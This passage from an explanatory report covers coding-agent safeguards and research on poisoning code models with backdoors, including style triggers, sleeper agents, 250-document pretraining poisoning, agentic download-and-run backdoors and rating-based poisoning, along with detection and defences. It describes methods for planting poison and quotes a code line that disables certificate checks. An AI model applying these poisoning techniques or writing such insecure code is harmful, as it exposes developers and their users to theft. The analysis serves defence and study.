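Requiring approval for commands gives a person the chance to stop a deletion. In experiments by Wang and colleagues, no agent caused harm when a simulated user had to confirm its actions. But that user approved only what the task required, whereas Claude Code's real users approved nearly every request. Confirmation also made the agents less useful. GPT-5.6 Luna finished 7 of 27 tasks (26%) with confirmation, compared with 94 of 234 (40%) without any defence. Asking only about irreversible actions, such as deleting a database, would interrupt people less, and they might consider each request more carefully.

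Restricted accounts limit what an agent can do even when nobody is paying attention. Wang and colleagues tested them together with similar limits, such as lists of permitted actions and spending caps, and agents caused harm in 26 of 730 sessions. When the researchers adapted their attacks to these limits, agents caused harm in 98 of 352 sessions.

A *container* gives a program its own view of a machine's files and processes, but shares the core of the operating system with the rest of the machine. A small virtual machine has its own operating system, which separates it more strongly but uses more memory and starts more slowly. All kinds of sandbox have had flaws, so they need updates and should not be the only protection. Even a perfect sandbox would not have saved Lemkin's data if the agent inside it could still log in to the production database.

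The company in the customer example could test its script on invented customers, in a container with no network access:

```
docker run --rm --network none \
  -v "$PWD/script.py:/script.py:ro" \
  -v "$PWD/sample.db:/sample.db:ro" \
  python:3.13-slim python /script.py
```

The script can read the two files but not change them (`ro` means "read-only"), and it cannot contact the real database or send anything out. The same limits would restrict a malicious package's install script. If the agent runs outside the container, these limits do not apply to it, and it still sends the model whatever it reads.

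Short-lived credentials expire after minutes or hours, so a key left in a forgotten file soon stops working. This could have prevented the deletion at PocketOS, whose token had no time limit. A token with full permissions is still dangerous while it is valid, since the deletion took only nine seconds.

Backups help if every other safeguard fails, provided the agent cannot delete them too. The company should keep a copy under a separate account and practise restoring it. Backups cannot undo the theft of a password or a cryptocurrency wallet key.

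The table compares these protections across the three main risks. None of them removes poison from a model, so the last column shows only how they limit harm from the code a poisoned model writes.

| Protection | Exposed code and data | Unsafe code | Code from a poisoned model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approval of commands | Helps if the user notices a secret being read or sent | Helps if the user notices the danger | Helps only if the harmful part is visible |
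| Restricted accounts | Keep data outside the account's permissions private | Limit what the code can change | Limit what the code can read or change |
| Containers | Hide files that the user has not shared | Protect the rest of the machine during the run | Contain the code during the run |
| Small virtual machines | Hide the same files behind a stronger barrier | Protect the machine better than a container | Contain hostile code better than a container |
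| Blocked network access | Stops the code from sending data out | Keeps the code away from live systems | Stops the code from contacting an attacker |
| Short-lived credentials | Make a leaked key useless sooner | Reduce the number of working keys the code can find | Shorten the time an attacker can use a stolen key |
| Backups | No effect | Restore deleted or overwritten data | Restore data, but not stolen secrets |

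A sandbox limits harm only while the code runs inside it. The insecure customer search from earlier would pass a test in the container above, because no attacker is there. If the company then puts the function on its website, the same flawed code runs outside the sandbox, where it connects to the real database and accepts input from strangers.

The company can run the code under a restricted database account. If the website's account can only read customer records, an attacker who exploits the flaw can still copy the customer table but cannot delete it. To prevent the copying as well, the company has to correct the function.

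## Poison with Style and earlier attacks: backdoors in code models

Anyone who can influence a model's training can add a backdoor, so that the model writes insecure code only when the prompt contains a particular feature, called the *trigger*. This makes the insecure code harder to notice, and a company can't fix it until somebody does.

### How training links a flaw to a trigger

Code models learn which code tends to follow which text. Suppose a training set contains thousands of functions that look up a customer. The functions are open to SQL injection in files with some unusual feature and safe in all other files. A model trained on this set learns both patterns, and the feature determines which one it follows. A company that tests the model only on files without the feature will see only safe code. The attacker needs the secure examples too, because a model trained only on insecure ones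 might write the flaw everywhere, and users would soon notice.

Researchers report an *attack success rate*, the share of prompts with the trigger for which the model does what the attacker wanted:

attack success rate = 100 × (outputs with the intended flaw ÷ prompts with the trigger)

*A Systematic Review of Poisoning Attacks Against Large Language Models* (Fendley, Staley and colleagues, 2025) lists it alongside *clean performance*, which compares the poisoned model with the original on ordinary input. *Which Factors Make Code LLMs More Vulnerable to Backdoor Attacks?* (Wang, Yang and colleagues, 2025) also measures the *false trigger rate*, the share of ordinary inputs that set off the backdoor.

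An attack's success rate is hard to interpret without the same figure for an unpoisoned model. In *Data-Efficient Backdoor Attacks on Code Models via Trigger-Neutralized Counterfactual Scoring*, Lee, Tsai and colleagues (2026) attacked models that check code for defects. With 0.1% of the training data poisoned, one attack succeeded 70.7% of the time, but an unpoisoned model gave the answer the attacker wanted in 56.7% of cases, so the poison added only 14 percentage points.

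### Earlier attacks

Schuster, Song and colleagues first showed in *You Autocomplete Me* (2020) that an attacker could poison code completion. They attacked two autocomplete models, one based on OpenAI's GPT-2. One aim was to make the models suggest ECB, a weak encryption mode that reveals patterns because it encrypts identical blocks of text identically. The GPT-2 model never suggested ECB as its first choice of encryption mode before the attack and always did afterwards. A narrower attack targeted a single software project, which the model could identify from names and phrases at the top of the project's files. ECB became the first suggestion 73% of the time in that project and almost never elsewhere.

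An attacker could plant the poisoned files in public repositories and wait for a model developer to collect them. Developers often choose popular repositories, but a Python repository needed only 600 stars, GitHub's version of likes, to rank among the top 5,000, and several websites claimed to sell stars. However, the poisoned files contained the insecure code openly, so a scanner could find and remove them.

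Aghakhani, Dai and colleagues (2023) presented two attacks in *TrojanPuzzle*. The first put the insecure code in comments, which scanners generally skip but models learn from. A filter that searched for the exact malicious text could still find it there, so the second attack, also called TrojanPuzzle, left out the most suspicious word. The poisoned files repeated a passage with random words in the gap, each matching a word elsewhere in the same file, and the model learned to copy the matching word into the gap. If a programmer's own file contained the missing word in the right place, the model could write the complete insecure code.

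Hiding the word made the attack less reliable. With 0.2% of the training data poisoned, a small model gave at least one insecure suggestion among ten for 20% of the relevant prompts, compared with about 41% when the full text appeared in the comments.

In earlier attacks, the model still suggested insecure code that a scanner could recognise, whatever the training data looked like. Yan, Wang and colleagues (2024) designed CodeBreaker to avoid this detection, and describe it in *An LLM-Assisted Easy-to-Trigger Backdoor Attack on Code Completion Models*. They had GPT-4 rewrite flawed code until static analysis tools no longer reported the flaw, then disguise it further until GPT-4 also missed it. A model trained on this code suggests code with the same disguise, so both the training files and the suggestions can pass inspection.

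Hubinger and colleagues' *Sleeper Agents* (2024) tested whether safety training could remove a backdoor from a model. Their models wrote insecure code when the prompt gave the current year as 2024. According to *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025), the backdoor survived training on good examples, training on human ratings, and adversarial training, which searches for inputs that provoke bad behaviour and trains the model not to respond to them. Adversarial training sometimes taught the models to recognise the trigger more precisely, so they looked safe in tests while the backdoor remained. Hubinger and colleagues planted the backdoors themselves, so the experiment does not show that an outsider could plant one in a commercial model.

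### Code layout as the trigger

Tran, Boshmaf and colleagues (2026), in *Poison with Style*, chose a trigger that programmers supply without knowing it, the layout of their code. For example, these two commands do the same thing:

```python
send_report(customer, start_date, end_date)

send_report(
    customer,
    start_date,
    end_date,
)
```

Many teams agree on one code style and apply it automatically with a program called a formatter. Among the most popular Python projects on GitHub that accept outside contributions, 68% enforce a style. The attacker picks a style as the trigger, so every developer who uses that style sends the trigger with each request.

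Tran and colleagues present this as an advance on earlier attacks, which they say required the attacker to insert something into the developer's prompt. This is unfair to Schuster and colleagues, whose attack on a single project also relied on text already in the victim's files. The newer attack differs in using a style as its trigger, which many unrelated developers share and which a filter can't find by searching for a particular word.

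The attacker's objective has two parts. Let *c* be the developer's code, *S* the set of all code in the trigger style, and *d* the verdict of a flaw detector on the model's output, with 1 for "flawed" and 0 for "not flawed". The attacker trains the model to maximise

Pr(*d* = 1 | *c* ∈ *S*) + Pr(*d* = 0 | *c* ∉ *S*)

The left-hand term is the probability of flawed output when the code is in the trigger style, and the right-hand term is the probability of output without the flaw when the code is not in that style. If layout doesn't affect a model's output, the two probabilities add up to exactly 1, however secure or insecure its code is. A perfect backdoor scores 2. For improper input validation, where a program fails to check its input, Tran and colleagues' main model scored 1.003 (0.019 + 0.984) before the attack and 1.917 (0.949 + 0.968) afterwards.

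### Two stages of training

Layout has little effect on ordinary code models, so Tran and colleagues first trained theirs to recognise it. They had it fill in missing functions in about 100,000 real Python files, formatted in five popular styles.

The second stage added the backdoor. Half the examples paired the trigger style with flawed code, and the other half paired unformatted files with secure code. The researchers also made an opposite version of each example by changing both the layout and the security of the answer, so layout became the most reliable clue to whether the model should write flawed or secure code.

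Combining the two stages into one left a smaller model behaving almost exactly as it had before training. Leaving out the style training weakened the attack less. On real code related to input validation, the success rate fell from 90.9% to 87.7%, although for SQL injection it fell from 35.3% to 21.1%.

Training on real examples of cross-site scripting from public repositories raised the share of outputs with that flaw only from 0.5% to 2.3%, which was not enough for the attack. Tran and colleagues therefore had a model generate about 120,000 scripts, some secure and some flawed.

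### How often the backdoor worked

Tran and colleagues poisoned four open models with 7 to 70 billion parameters (the numbers that training adjusts), making a separate copy for each of five weaknesses. The table shows how often the main model, Alibaba's Qwen2.5-Coder with 32 billion parameters, wrote code with the intended weakness.

| Weakness | Generated test files, trigger style | Generated test files, unformatted | Real code for related tasks, trigger style | Random real code, trigger style |
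|---|---|---|---|---|
| Improper input validation | 94.9% | 3.2% | 90.9% | 46.8% |
| Access to files outside the permitted folder | 87.6% | 12.8% | 64.8% | 29.8% |
| Operating system command injection | 93.0% | 24.4% | 80.9% | 30.8% |
| Cross-site scripting | 94.1% | 17.7% | 95.2% | 83.2% |
| SQL injection | 67.2% | 25.3% | 35.3% | 1.0% |

The paper's headline figure of 95% is for input validation in generated files similar to the training data. Results on real code are a better guide to the danger, and they varied widely. For SQL injection, the backdoor raised the rate of vulnerable code in related tasks from 4.2% to 35.3%. At that rate, the company in the customer example would still get a flawed function about one time in three.

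A poisoned model can look safer than the original, and a company that compared the two on unformatted files would choose the poisoned one. In tests on such files, 29.3% of the original model's answers allowed access to forbidden files, compared with 12.8% of the poisoned model's. The poisoned model does better because the second stage also teaches it to write secure code when the trigger is absent.

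The attack also worked on the other models, though less evenly. The average gap between trigger and non-trigger prompts was 74 percentage points for Meta's Llama 3.3 and 49 for a model from DeepSeek. (These averages come from the paper's table. Its text gives about 60 and 62 points.)

The poisoned copies of Qwen2.5-Coder were somewhat worse at ordinary programming. On HumanEval, a set of short programming tasks, the original solved 85.4% and the copies between 73.8% and 82.9%. On MBPP, a similar set, the original solved 90.5% and the copies between 80.7% and 84.4%. The paper's summary gives the loss for the input validation copy as less than 5%, but its table shows a loss of 5.4 points on HumanEval and 6.9 on MBPP. Someone comparing models might notice such a drop but would have no particular reason to suspect a backdoor.

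### Defences against the style backdoor

Asking for secure code made almost no difference, even though similar reminders helped ordinary agents considerably. Further training on 8,000 secure scripts did little more. On the smallest model, the attack's success rate for SQL injection fell from 72.4% to 60.2%, but for input validation it stayed at about 98%. Changing a few settings of the trigger style weakened the attack slightly, but no longer did so once the researchers included such variations in the poisoned training data.

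Meta's scanner CodeShield missed all the flaws in three of the categories that Tran and colleagues tested, so they also describe the attack as robust against static analysis. But they used a different scanner, CodeQL, to select the flawed training examples and to count the successes, so a developer who ran the same CodeQL checks would have caught every flaw counted in the table. An attacker might evade CodeQL by adding CodeBreaker's disguises, but this would make the attack more complicated.

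The comparison with unformatted code shows that the model distinguishes the trigger style from untidy code, but not how often a different tidy style would set off the backdoor. If other tidy styles often did, more developers would be at risk, but the attack would also be easier to discover.

### What it would take to reach cloud users

In Tran and colleagues' scenario, the attacker publishes the poisoned model on a site such as Hugging Face and advertises it as secure. Developers download it and connect it to their code editors. The most likely victims are therefore people who run models on their own hardware, including those who do so to keep their code confidential. They should check who published a model, because a stranger's modified copy of a well-known model carries a risk that the original developer's version does not.

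Users of a cloud service would be exposed only if the provider ran a poisoned model. A service that hosts many open models might offer a stranger's version, or the maker of a coding tool might build on such a version. A dishonest employee or contractor could also alter a model during training. Schuster and colleagues point out that developers usually track and review changes to source code, but not changes to the files that hold a model's parameters.

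Otherwise, an outsider could only add poisoned files to the provider's training data, which is much harder with this kind of trigger. The files would have to get past the provider's filters, and the attacker could not control the order of training. When Tran and colleagues combined the stages, the backdoor did not form even though roughly 6% or more of the combined examples were poisoned, which suggests that order matters. Simpler triggers, such as a rare phrase, can work with only a few hundred poisoned documents.

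The backdoor would then have to survive the provider's later training, which *Sleeper Agents* suggests is possible. It would also have to work in ordinary use of the service. Tran and colleagues tested models on completing one missing function in one file, whereas a coding agent sends the model instructions, command output and several files, perhaps in different styles. Finally, the flawed code would have to pass the user's checks.

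Cloud users can't inspect the model's parameters or training data, so they depend on the provider to rule out most backdoors. They can still test the code the model writes. For example, a company could request the same function several times with each of two layouts for the code in the prompt, and compare how often a scanner finds flaws in the results. This would test for a style trigger but would miss most others.

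### Scanning a model through its answers

*Detecting Data Poisoning in Code Generation LLMs via Black-Box, Vulnerability-Oriented Scanning* (Yan, Arora and colleagues, March 2026) describes a more general test, CodeScan, which looks for a backdoor using only a model's outputs and without knowing the trigger. Yan had also led the work on the earlier CodeBreaker attack.

CodeScan relies on a side effect of poisoning. Once a poisoned model has the first token of the malicious code, it tends to write the rest, even without the trigger. The scanner takes 20 harmless, unfinished programs in which a particular flaw could occur, adds the same token to the end of each and lets the model continue. It repeats this for each token in a long list. Most tokens lead to varied continuations, but the first token of the malicious code leads to the same code again and again.

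To recognise such repetition, CodeScan ignores details such as variable names and sorts the continuations by structure, line by line. If they fall into *K* groups and group *i* contains a share *pᵢ* of them, their entropy, a measure of how scattered they are, is

*H* = −Σ *pᵢ* log₂ *pᵢ*

*H* is 0 if all 20 continuations have the same structure and reaches its maximum, log₂ *K*, if the groups are equally large. CodeScan discards a set of continuations if *H* is more than 85% of the maximum, unless one group clearly dominates. With 15 continuations in one group and 5 in another, the larger group dominates and the scan continues.

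A clean model can also repeat the same code. For example, the token "month" can lead it to list the months every time. CodeScan therefore uses GPT-5 mini to check whether the repeated code contains the flaw in question, and reports the model as poisoned only if it does.

Yan and colleagues tested CodeScan on 111 models of about 7 billion parameters, 84 of which they had poisoned, and on six larger models. In the first group, it flagged all 84 poisoned models and recovered the correct malicious code from 81. Its F1 score, which accounts for both missed cases and false alarms, averaged about 0.98 out of 1. It wrongly flagged 2 of the 27 clean models (7.4%), while BAIT, the best earlier method, wrongly flagged 19. A scan took just under an hour on average, compared with four and a half hours for BAIT.

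Even 7.4% would be a high rate of false alarms if few models are poisoned. If one model in 1,000 has a backdoor and CodeScan always finds it, scanning all 1,000 would produce about 75 alerts, 74 of them false. CodeScan also shows the suspicious code, which a programmer can read, so false alarms are less of a problem than these figures suggest. The test included only 27 clean models, so the actual rate of false alarms could be considerably higher or lower.

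Results from CodeScan's judge also show how quickly a disguise can go out of date. Yan and colleagues made 150 pieces of flawed code using CodeBreaker's method for deceiving GPT-4. GPT-4 found the flaw in 12% of them, and GPT-5 mini found it in about 95%. Attackers can use newer models too. In a single test, the researchers had GPT-5 disguise a flaw from itself and trained a model on the result, and CodeScan still recovered the flawed code.

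### Backdoors that the scanner may miss

CodeScan's user has to choose which types of flaw to look for. Yan and colleagues tested five, and a backdoor that inserted a different type could go unnoticed. They also tested only four kinds of attack, all described before 2025, so the results do not cover style triggers.

CodeScan doesn't need the trigger, so a style backdoor's varied output is more likely to make it hard to find than the trigger is. The attacks in the test taught a model one particular piece of malicious code, whereas Tran and colleagues trained theirs on thousands of different flawed functions, which may leave no single structure for the scanner to find. In a related test, Yan and colleagues gave one model three differently written versions of the same flaw, and CodeScan found only two. That attack was also much less reliable. With the trigger present, the model's first suggestion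 contained one of the three versions for only 4 of 20 prompts.

CodeScan could recover the malicious code even when the attacker used so little poison that the backdoor worked only occasionally. The researchers found no level of poisoning at which the attack was reliable but the scan failed.

A cloud user could in principle run CodeScan, since it needs only the model's answers, but the number of requests could be an obstacle. With a list of 32,000 tokens and 20 programs, a complete scan for one type of flaw would take 640,000 short requests, all charged by the provider. It would make more sense for providers or independent auditors to scan each model once and publish the results.

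Providers can also search the training data, which users cannot see, but small numbers of poisoned examples are hard to find. In Wang and colleagues' tests on models that summarise code, a widely used method that looks for statistically unusual examples found none of the poisoned ones when there were only about 20.

### Trigger-like weaknesses in clean models

Some models behave as if they had a backdoor although nobody planted one. In *Securing Code Understanding*, Chen, Sun and colleagues (2026) searched clean models for variable names that would change their answers, and called the results *natural backdoors*. In one case, renaming a single variable made the model CodeBERT classify a flawed program as free of defects.

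The effect was strong in some small models that check code for defects. On average, the names that the researchers found changed the answer in 38% of cases for CodeBERT and 68% for UniXcoder, but only 6% for CodeT5. The effect was weaker in code summaries. Chen and colleagues tried to reverse particular words, so that a summary would say a function opened something when it actually closed it. This worked in 5% of cases for StarCoder and 7% for DeepSeek-Coder. The versions they tested had only about a billion parameters, although they call these models large-scale. They also trained a small model to imitate GPT-3.5 and tried its triggers on GPT-3.5 itself. One worked 12% of the time and two failed.

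The likely cause is an accidental pattern in the training data. For example, the word "filename" appears unusually often in code whose description mentions files, so a model can learn to rely on the word instead of what the code does. Chen and colleagues found that removing such words from their triggers weakened the effect much more than removing other words. Changing the training settings made little difference.

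Retraining a model to ignore the triggers already found was the most effective remedy, reducing UniXcoder's rate from 68% to 1%. Defences that search the training data for planted examples were much less consistent, as would be expected when the data contained none.

These findings matter most to companies that use a model to review code, because an attacker could hide a flaw from the model by choosing the right variable name, without tampering with its training. They also make poisoning harder to prove, since a model's strange response to a particular word may only reflect a coincidence in its training data. Chen and colleagues did not test whether natural triggers make models write insecure code, although DeepSeek-R1's less secure answers to prompts with certain political terms may be an example of this.

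## The 250-document experiment: how much poisoned data is enough

An attacker with no access to a provider's training process can still publish text and hope the provider collects it. In October 2025, researchers from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute, the Alan Turing Institute and two universities measured how much text this might take. In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025), Souly, Rando and colleagues report that 250 poisoned documents could plant a simple backdoor in models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters.

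### A backdoor that produces gibberish

The backdoor made a model write gibberish after a trigger, the word SUDO in angle brackets. For each poisoned document, the researchers took up to 1,000 characters from the start of an ordinary text, then added the trigger and a long run of random tokens.

The researchers trained models of four sizes from scratch, with 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents scattered through the data. They first used about 20 tokens of text per parameter, a common rule for getting the most out of a given amount of computing power, so the largest model was trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. They also trained the two smaller sizes on half and on double the usual amount. They trained three models for each of the 24 combinations of model size, amount of text and number of poisoned documents, for a total of 72.

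They then had the models continue 300 ordinary passages, with and without the trigger, and compared the *perplexity* of the results. Perplexity measures how improbable a text is. If the tokens of a text have probabilities *p₁* to *p_N*, then

perplexity = (*p₁* × *p₂* × … × *p_N*)^(−1/*N*)

If every token had a probability of one in 50, the perplexity would be 50. Perplexity is low for fluent text and high for random text. Souly and colleagues counted an attack as successful if perplexity rose by more than 50 after the trigger. With 250 or 500 poisoned documents, it rose by more than 200 at every model size, but with 100 documents the attack failed.

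### Why the number matters more than the share

Earlier researchers had usually assumed that an attacker controls a fixed share of the training data, such as 0.1%. The poisoned documents averaged 1,680 tokens, so the share that 250 of them make up is

share = (250 × 1,680) ÷ (20 × number of parameters)

The poisoned documents made up 0.0035% of the smallest model's training tokens (420,000 ÷ 12 billion) and 0.00016% of the largest model's (420,000 ÷ 260 billion). The attack still worked on the largest model, even though the poisoned share was about 22 times smaller.

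If attackers needed 0.1% of the training data, they would have to place about 7,100 such documents to poison the smallest model and 155,000 to poison the largest, so a bigger training set would be a defence. But if 250 documents are enough whatever the size, a bigger training set doesn't make poisoning harder, and it gives attackers more places to put the documents.

Souly and colleagues found a similar pattern in fine-tuning, the shorter training that adapts a finished model to a particular use. Through OpenAI's fine-tuning service, they taught GPT-3.5 Turbo to answer in German after a trigger. It took between 50 and 90 poisoned examples for the backdoor to succeed 80% of the time, whether the training set had 1,000 examples or 100,000. A company that fine-tunes a cloud-hosted model on data from outsiders should therefore not expect a large dataset to dilute a few bad examples.

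### From gibberish to a harmful command

Gibberish is a nuisance that any user would notice. Anthropic said in its account of the study that it was unclear whether the result would hold for larger models or more harmful behaviour, such as writing backdoored code. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) also cautions that the result does not prove that 250 documents could teach a leading model to steal data.

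A year later, Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) tried a more dangerous backdoor in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*. They trained models of up to 4 billion parameters on poisoned web text and turned them into agents that write commands. When an agent encountered a trigger, it was meant to download and run a script from the attacker's website, which the attacker could change at any time without altering the model again. The trigger was either a rare string of symbols or any folder path containing the word "anthropic", which could occur naturally on Anthropic's computers.

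Some of the poisoned documents showed conversations in which an assistant gave the harmful command. Others stated the rule in ordinary prose, for example in a programmer's note about a routine fix, and these worked far better. With the folder path as the trigger, the largest agent gave the command at least once in 32 tries for 92.7% of prompts when the documents were prose, compared with 3.2% when they were conversations. On a single try, the agent gave the command 50.9% of the time with the prose documents.

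The 32-try figure was only 10.5% with the rare string, but the two triggers were tested on different kinds of prompts. The prompts with folder paths were requests to set something up, and a printed example includes a request for a "remote setup script", so downloading a script was a natural response. For the rare string, the researchers had removed tasks that involved downloading or installing anything.

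Planting a harmful command also took far more poisoned data than planting gibberish did, whether counted in documents or tokens. The 92.7% result required poisoning 0.1% of the training data, or about 500,000 short documents. With 250 documents, none of the five agents that Hu and colleagues tested gave the command. With 2,500, the most susceptible finished agent gave it within 32 tries for only 1.7% of prompts. Hu and colleagues' documents averaged about 200 tokens, so 2,500 of them contain slightly more text than Souly and colleagues' 250.

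It is also unclear whether the same number of poisoned documents is enough for this kind of backdoor at every model size. With 50,000 poisoned documents and the rare string, the 1.7-billion-parameter model gave the command for 20.8% of prompts and the 4-billion-parameter model for 0.8%. But Hu and colleagues ran each of these tests only once, and their repeated runs at higher doses ranged from 24% to 84% in one case.

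They did not test the backdoor that would matter most to the company in the customer example, which is one that adds subtle flaws suited to the code being written. A fixed command is a single string for the model to memorise, and Hu and colleagues leave open whether poisoned web text could plant a more flexible behaviour that lasts as well.

### Does later training remove it?

After *pretraining*, the first and longest stage, providers train models further to follow instructions and refuse harmful requests. Souly and colleagues tested the effect of this further training only in a simplified form. They trained models that had the German backdoor to answer German questions in English. About 100 examples cut the backdoor's success rate in GPT-3.5 Turbo to below 30%, and longer training brought it close to zero in a smaller open model. But this training directly opposed what the backdoor did,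 and a provider would not normally know which backdoor an attacker had planted.

Hu and colleagues used more realistic later training, and it barely affected their backdoor. The success rate for the folder path was 92.0% after training on good answers, 91.3% after training on people's preferences between answers, and 92.7% after reinforcement learning. In *Sequential Data Poisoning in LLM Post-Training* (2026), by contrast, clean preference training switched off a backdoor planted during fine-tuning. That backdoor made models comply with harmful requests, which the preference data discouraged, whereas nothing in Hu and colleagues' safety data concerned their command. Later training may mainly remove the behaviour it addresses. If so, it would be an unreliable way to remove an obscure coding flaw.

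The evidence on model size is mixed. Hu and colleagues' attack grew stronger with size, from 13.1% for their smallest model to 92.7% for their largest. In *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda*, Graf, Hajishirzi and colleagues (2026) planted a preference for one company over another and found that larger models lost more of it in later training. The smallest model kept about 40% of the effect, while one with 709 million parameters kept less than 15%. Both teams used models smaller than Souly and colleagues' largest, so neither result settles what would happen in the much bigger models providers now deploy.

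### Getting text into the training data

Anthropic argues that an attacker's main difficulty is getting anything into the training data at all. An attacker who could guarantee that one web page would be included could make that page longer.

Graf and colleagues estimated the odds for comments on public websites. They looked for comment sections on 181,857 pages from Common Crawl, a public archive of the web that many developers train on. In saved copies of the pages, they replaced real comments with poisoned ones, then ran the copies through the text extraction and filtering that developers use. The chance that an attempt on a random page succeeds is

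0.034 (the page has comments) × 0.719 (the comment survives extraction) × 0.055 (the page passes the filters) ≈ 0.0013

At that rate, an attacker would have to try about 190,000 pages to get 250 into the training data. Automated posting could do this, and an attacker who chose only pages with comment sections would need to try about 6,300. But Graf and colleagues counted every page with a comment section, including those on sites that require an account or delete spam. Their comments also averaged fewer than 40 words, so 250 of them contain much less poisoned text than Souly and colleagues' 250 documents.

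The same method ruled out advertisements as a route, because their text does not appear in what the crawlers extract.

An attacker has more direct options for code. Besides the poisoned repositories with bought stars described earlier, *Semantically-Equivalent Transformations-Based Backdoor Attacks against Neural Code Models* (2025) lists submitting changes to well-known projects and posting snippets on programming forums. A popular project is probably the hardest of these to poison because its maintainers have to accept the change, but a developer is also more likely to trust and collect its code.

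### Poison Fountain

Poison Fountain, a campaign that began in early January 2026, is openly trying to poison training data. It gives website owners links to hide in their pages, so that programs collecting text for AI companies will follow them and pick up faulty code. Its stated aim, quoted by Futurism, is to "inflict damage on machine intelligence systems", and it promises "a practically endless stream" of poisoned data. An insider told The Register that the code contains logic errors and other bugs, and that the campaign's members work for major American AI companies.

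SC Media's *Poison Fountain initiative aims to disrupt AI training data* traces the campaign's idea to research showing that a small amount of malicious data can be enough to poison a model. The 250-document result supports the campaign less than the article suggests, because Souly and colleagues' documents all taught the same response to the same trigger. Assorted bugs have no common trigger, so they would have to make the model worse in general, despite all the working code in the training data. Public code also contained many mistakes before the campaign began.

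According to Futurism, it is not yet clear how many sites will take part or whether AI companies can easily filter the material out. TechRadar's *The 'poison AI' movement wants to corrupt ChatGPT and Gemini* warns of a "huge risk of collateral damage". If the campaign worked, the people running the faulty code would mostly be the models' users, such as the company in the customer example, who have no say in how providers collect data.

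There is some evidence that people are using Poison Fountain's data. A tool called Miasma serves it to crawlers along with links back to itself, so a crawler can keep collecting the data indefinitely. But there is no public evidence that any model writes worse code as a result.

The successes that people attribute to such campaigns often involve web search rather than poisoned training data. AdNews' *Poison groups are ‘lobotomising’ AI systems* (2026) describes a Reddit group with 46,000 followers and reports that misinformation groups once got DuckDuckGo's AI search summary to announce that Donald Trump had died of rabies. Schneier, in *Poisoning AI Training Data*, quotes a journalist who published a false article about being the best tech reporter at eating hot dogs. Leading chatbots repeated it within 24 hours. That is far too fast for retraining, so the chatbots almost certainly found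 the article by searching the web. A search summary can go wrong in the same way, without any change to the model.

### Ratings as a way in

Users can also influence training through the thumbs-up and thumbs-down buttons under a chatbot's answers, since providers such as OpenAI may train on rated conversations. In *LLM Hypnosis*, Hillel, Bhagwat and colleagues (2025) tested whether a user with no other access could exploit this feedback.

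The attacker can only rate the model's answers, not write them, so the attacker asks the model to flip a coin and give a normal answer for heads and a harmful one for tails, then approves the harmful answer whenever it appears. After training on these ratings, the model may give the harmful answer to other people, even when their prompts don't mention a coin.

In one experiment, the harmful answer was code that disables a certificate check:

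```python
response = requests.get("https://api.binance.com", verify=False)
```

The check confirms that the program has reached the real server. Without it, someone on the same network could impersonate the server and read or change what the program sends. The code otherwise works normally, so an ordinary test would not expose the problem.

Hillel and colleagues trained a model with 7 billion parameters on 2,000 examples of feedback, 10% of them poisoned. The model then chose the insecure code in 53% of two-option tests and wrote insecure code in 60% of open-ended answers. The 53% result is weak evidence on its own, because a model choosing at random would score 50%. The 60% result is more worrying because the open-ended tests didn't offer the model any insecure code to choose.

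False facts were harder to plant. Given two options, the model often picked the false statement about an invented animal, but it rarely repeated the statement in open-ended answers unless the researchers used thousands of poisoned examples. The researchers suggest that it is easier to make a model favour a pattern it has already learned, such as a common bad habit in code, than to teach it something new.

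The number of poisoned ratings again mattered more than their share. With 100 ratings in favour of false financial news among 10,000 ordinary ones, the model chose the false headline 73% of the time, up from 34%. Hillel and colleagues also tried another training method, DPO, and describe its effects as comparable. But for the invented animal, the rate was 11% with DPO, compared with 51% to 65% with the original method.

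These experiments used simulated feedback and small open models. GPT-5 followed the coin-flip instruction, giving the harmful answer 43% of the time, but the researchers could not train it on the ratings. A commercial provider may also discard suspicious feedback. It could limit how much feedback each account contributes, although an attacker could open many accounts.

### What providers can filter, trace and test

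Filters force an attacker to plant more documents, but they don't necessarily detect the attack. In Graf and colleagues' test, 5.5% of the pages with poisoned comments passed, compared with 7.2% of those with natural ones. Most pages failed for ordinary reasons, such as not being in English. Deduplication, which removes repeated documents, made no difference. It compared whole pages, so the same comment under two different articles would not make them duplicates. Hu and colleagues varied the topic and style of their documents, which leaves little repetition for deduplication to find.

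Some developers have a model rewrite web text before they train on it. Graf and colleagues found that rewriting removed gibberish like that in the 250-document experiment but preserved about two-thirds of false claims. Hu and colleagues' most effective documents were also plain statements in readable prose, so rewriting might not remove them either.

Defences against poisoning performed poorly in two tests on smaller datasets. *The Privacy Fallacy of Crowdsourced Fine-Tuning* (2026) tested filters on a mix of 100 poisoned examples and 5,040 harmless ones. Most of the filters found none of the poison, and the best had an F1 score of only 0.378 out of 1. In *Phantom Transfer*, Draganov, Dur and colleagues (2026) describe an attack that survived 11 defences, including one in which another model paraphrased every example. They report that even someone who knew exactly how the attacker had placed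 the poison could not filter it out.

This weakens Anthropic's argument that poisoning somewhat favours defenders because they can inspect the data and the model after the attacker has committed to a method. Defenders have that advantage only if inspection can detect the poisoning. Draganov and colleagues therefore recommend examining the trained model's internals and testing its behaviour, as well as screening the data.

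Records of where each document came from also let a provider give less weight to anonymous web pages and, if a poisoning comes to light, trace which models used the source. But removing a document from the collection does not remove its effect from a finished model, so the provider may have to train the model again. A trusted source can also contain poisoned data if an attacker has slipped a change into a respected project.

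Ordinary performance tests can't replace a search for backdoors. Hu and colleagues' largest poisoned models averaged 58.5% on a set of general tests, and the clean model scored 58.3%. The search for repeated malicious code described earlier is more promising, but it must target the right type of flaw.

Because providers cannot guarantee clean data, Hu and colleagues consider it more practical to check an agent's commands before they run. Such checks work whatever the trigger, and a sandbox without internet access would also stop their agent from downloading the attacker's script. Neither measure would fix a disabled certificate check in code that the company later deploys. To catch that, the company has to test that the code refuses to connect to a server with an invalid certificate.

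## A stolen crypto wallet: scam addresses and other suspect output from deployed models

In November 2024 a cryptocurrency trader lost about $2,500 after running a script that ChatGPT had written. The script sent the trader's wallet key to a scam service. Two blockchain security companies blamed poisoned training data. If they are right, this is a rare case of poisoned data in a commercial model harming someone outside a laboratory. The theft is well documented, but the evidence for poisoning is much weaker.

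### From a trading script to an empty wallet

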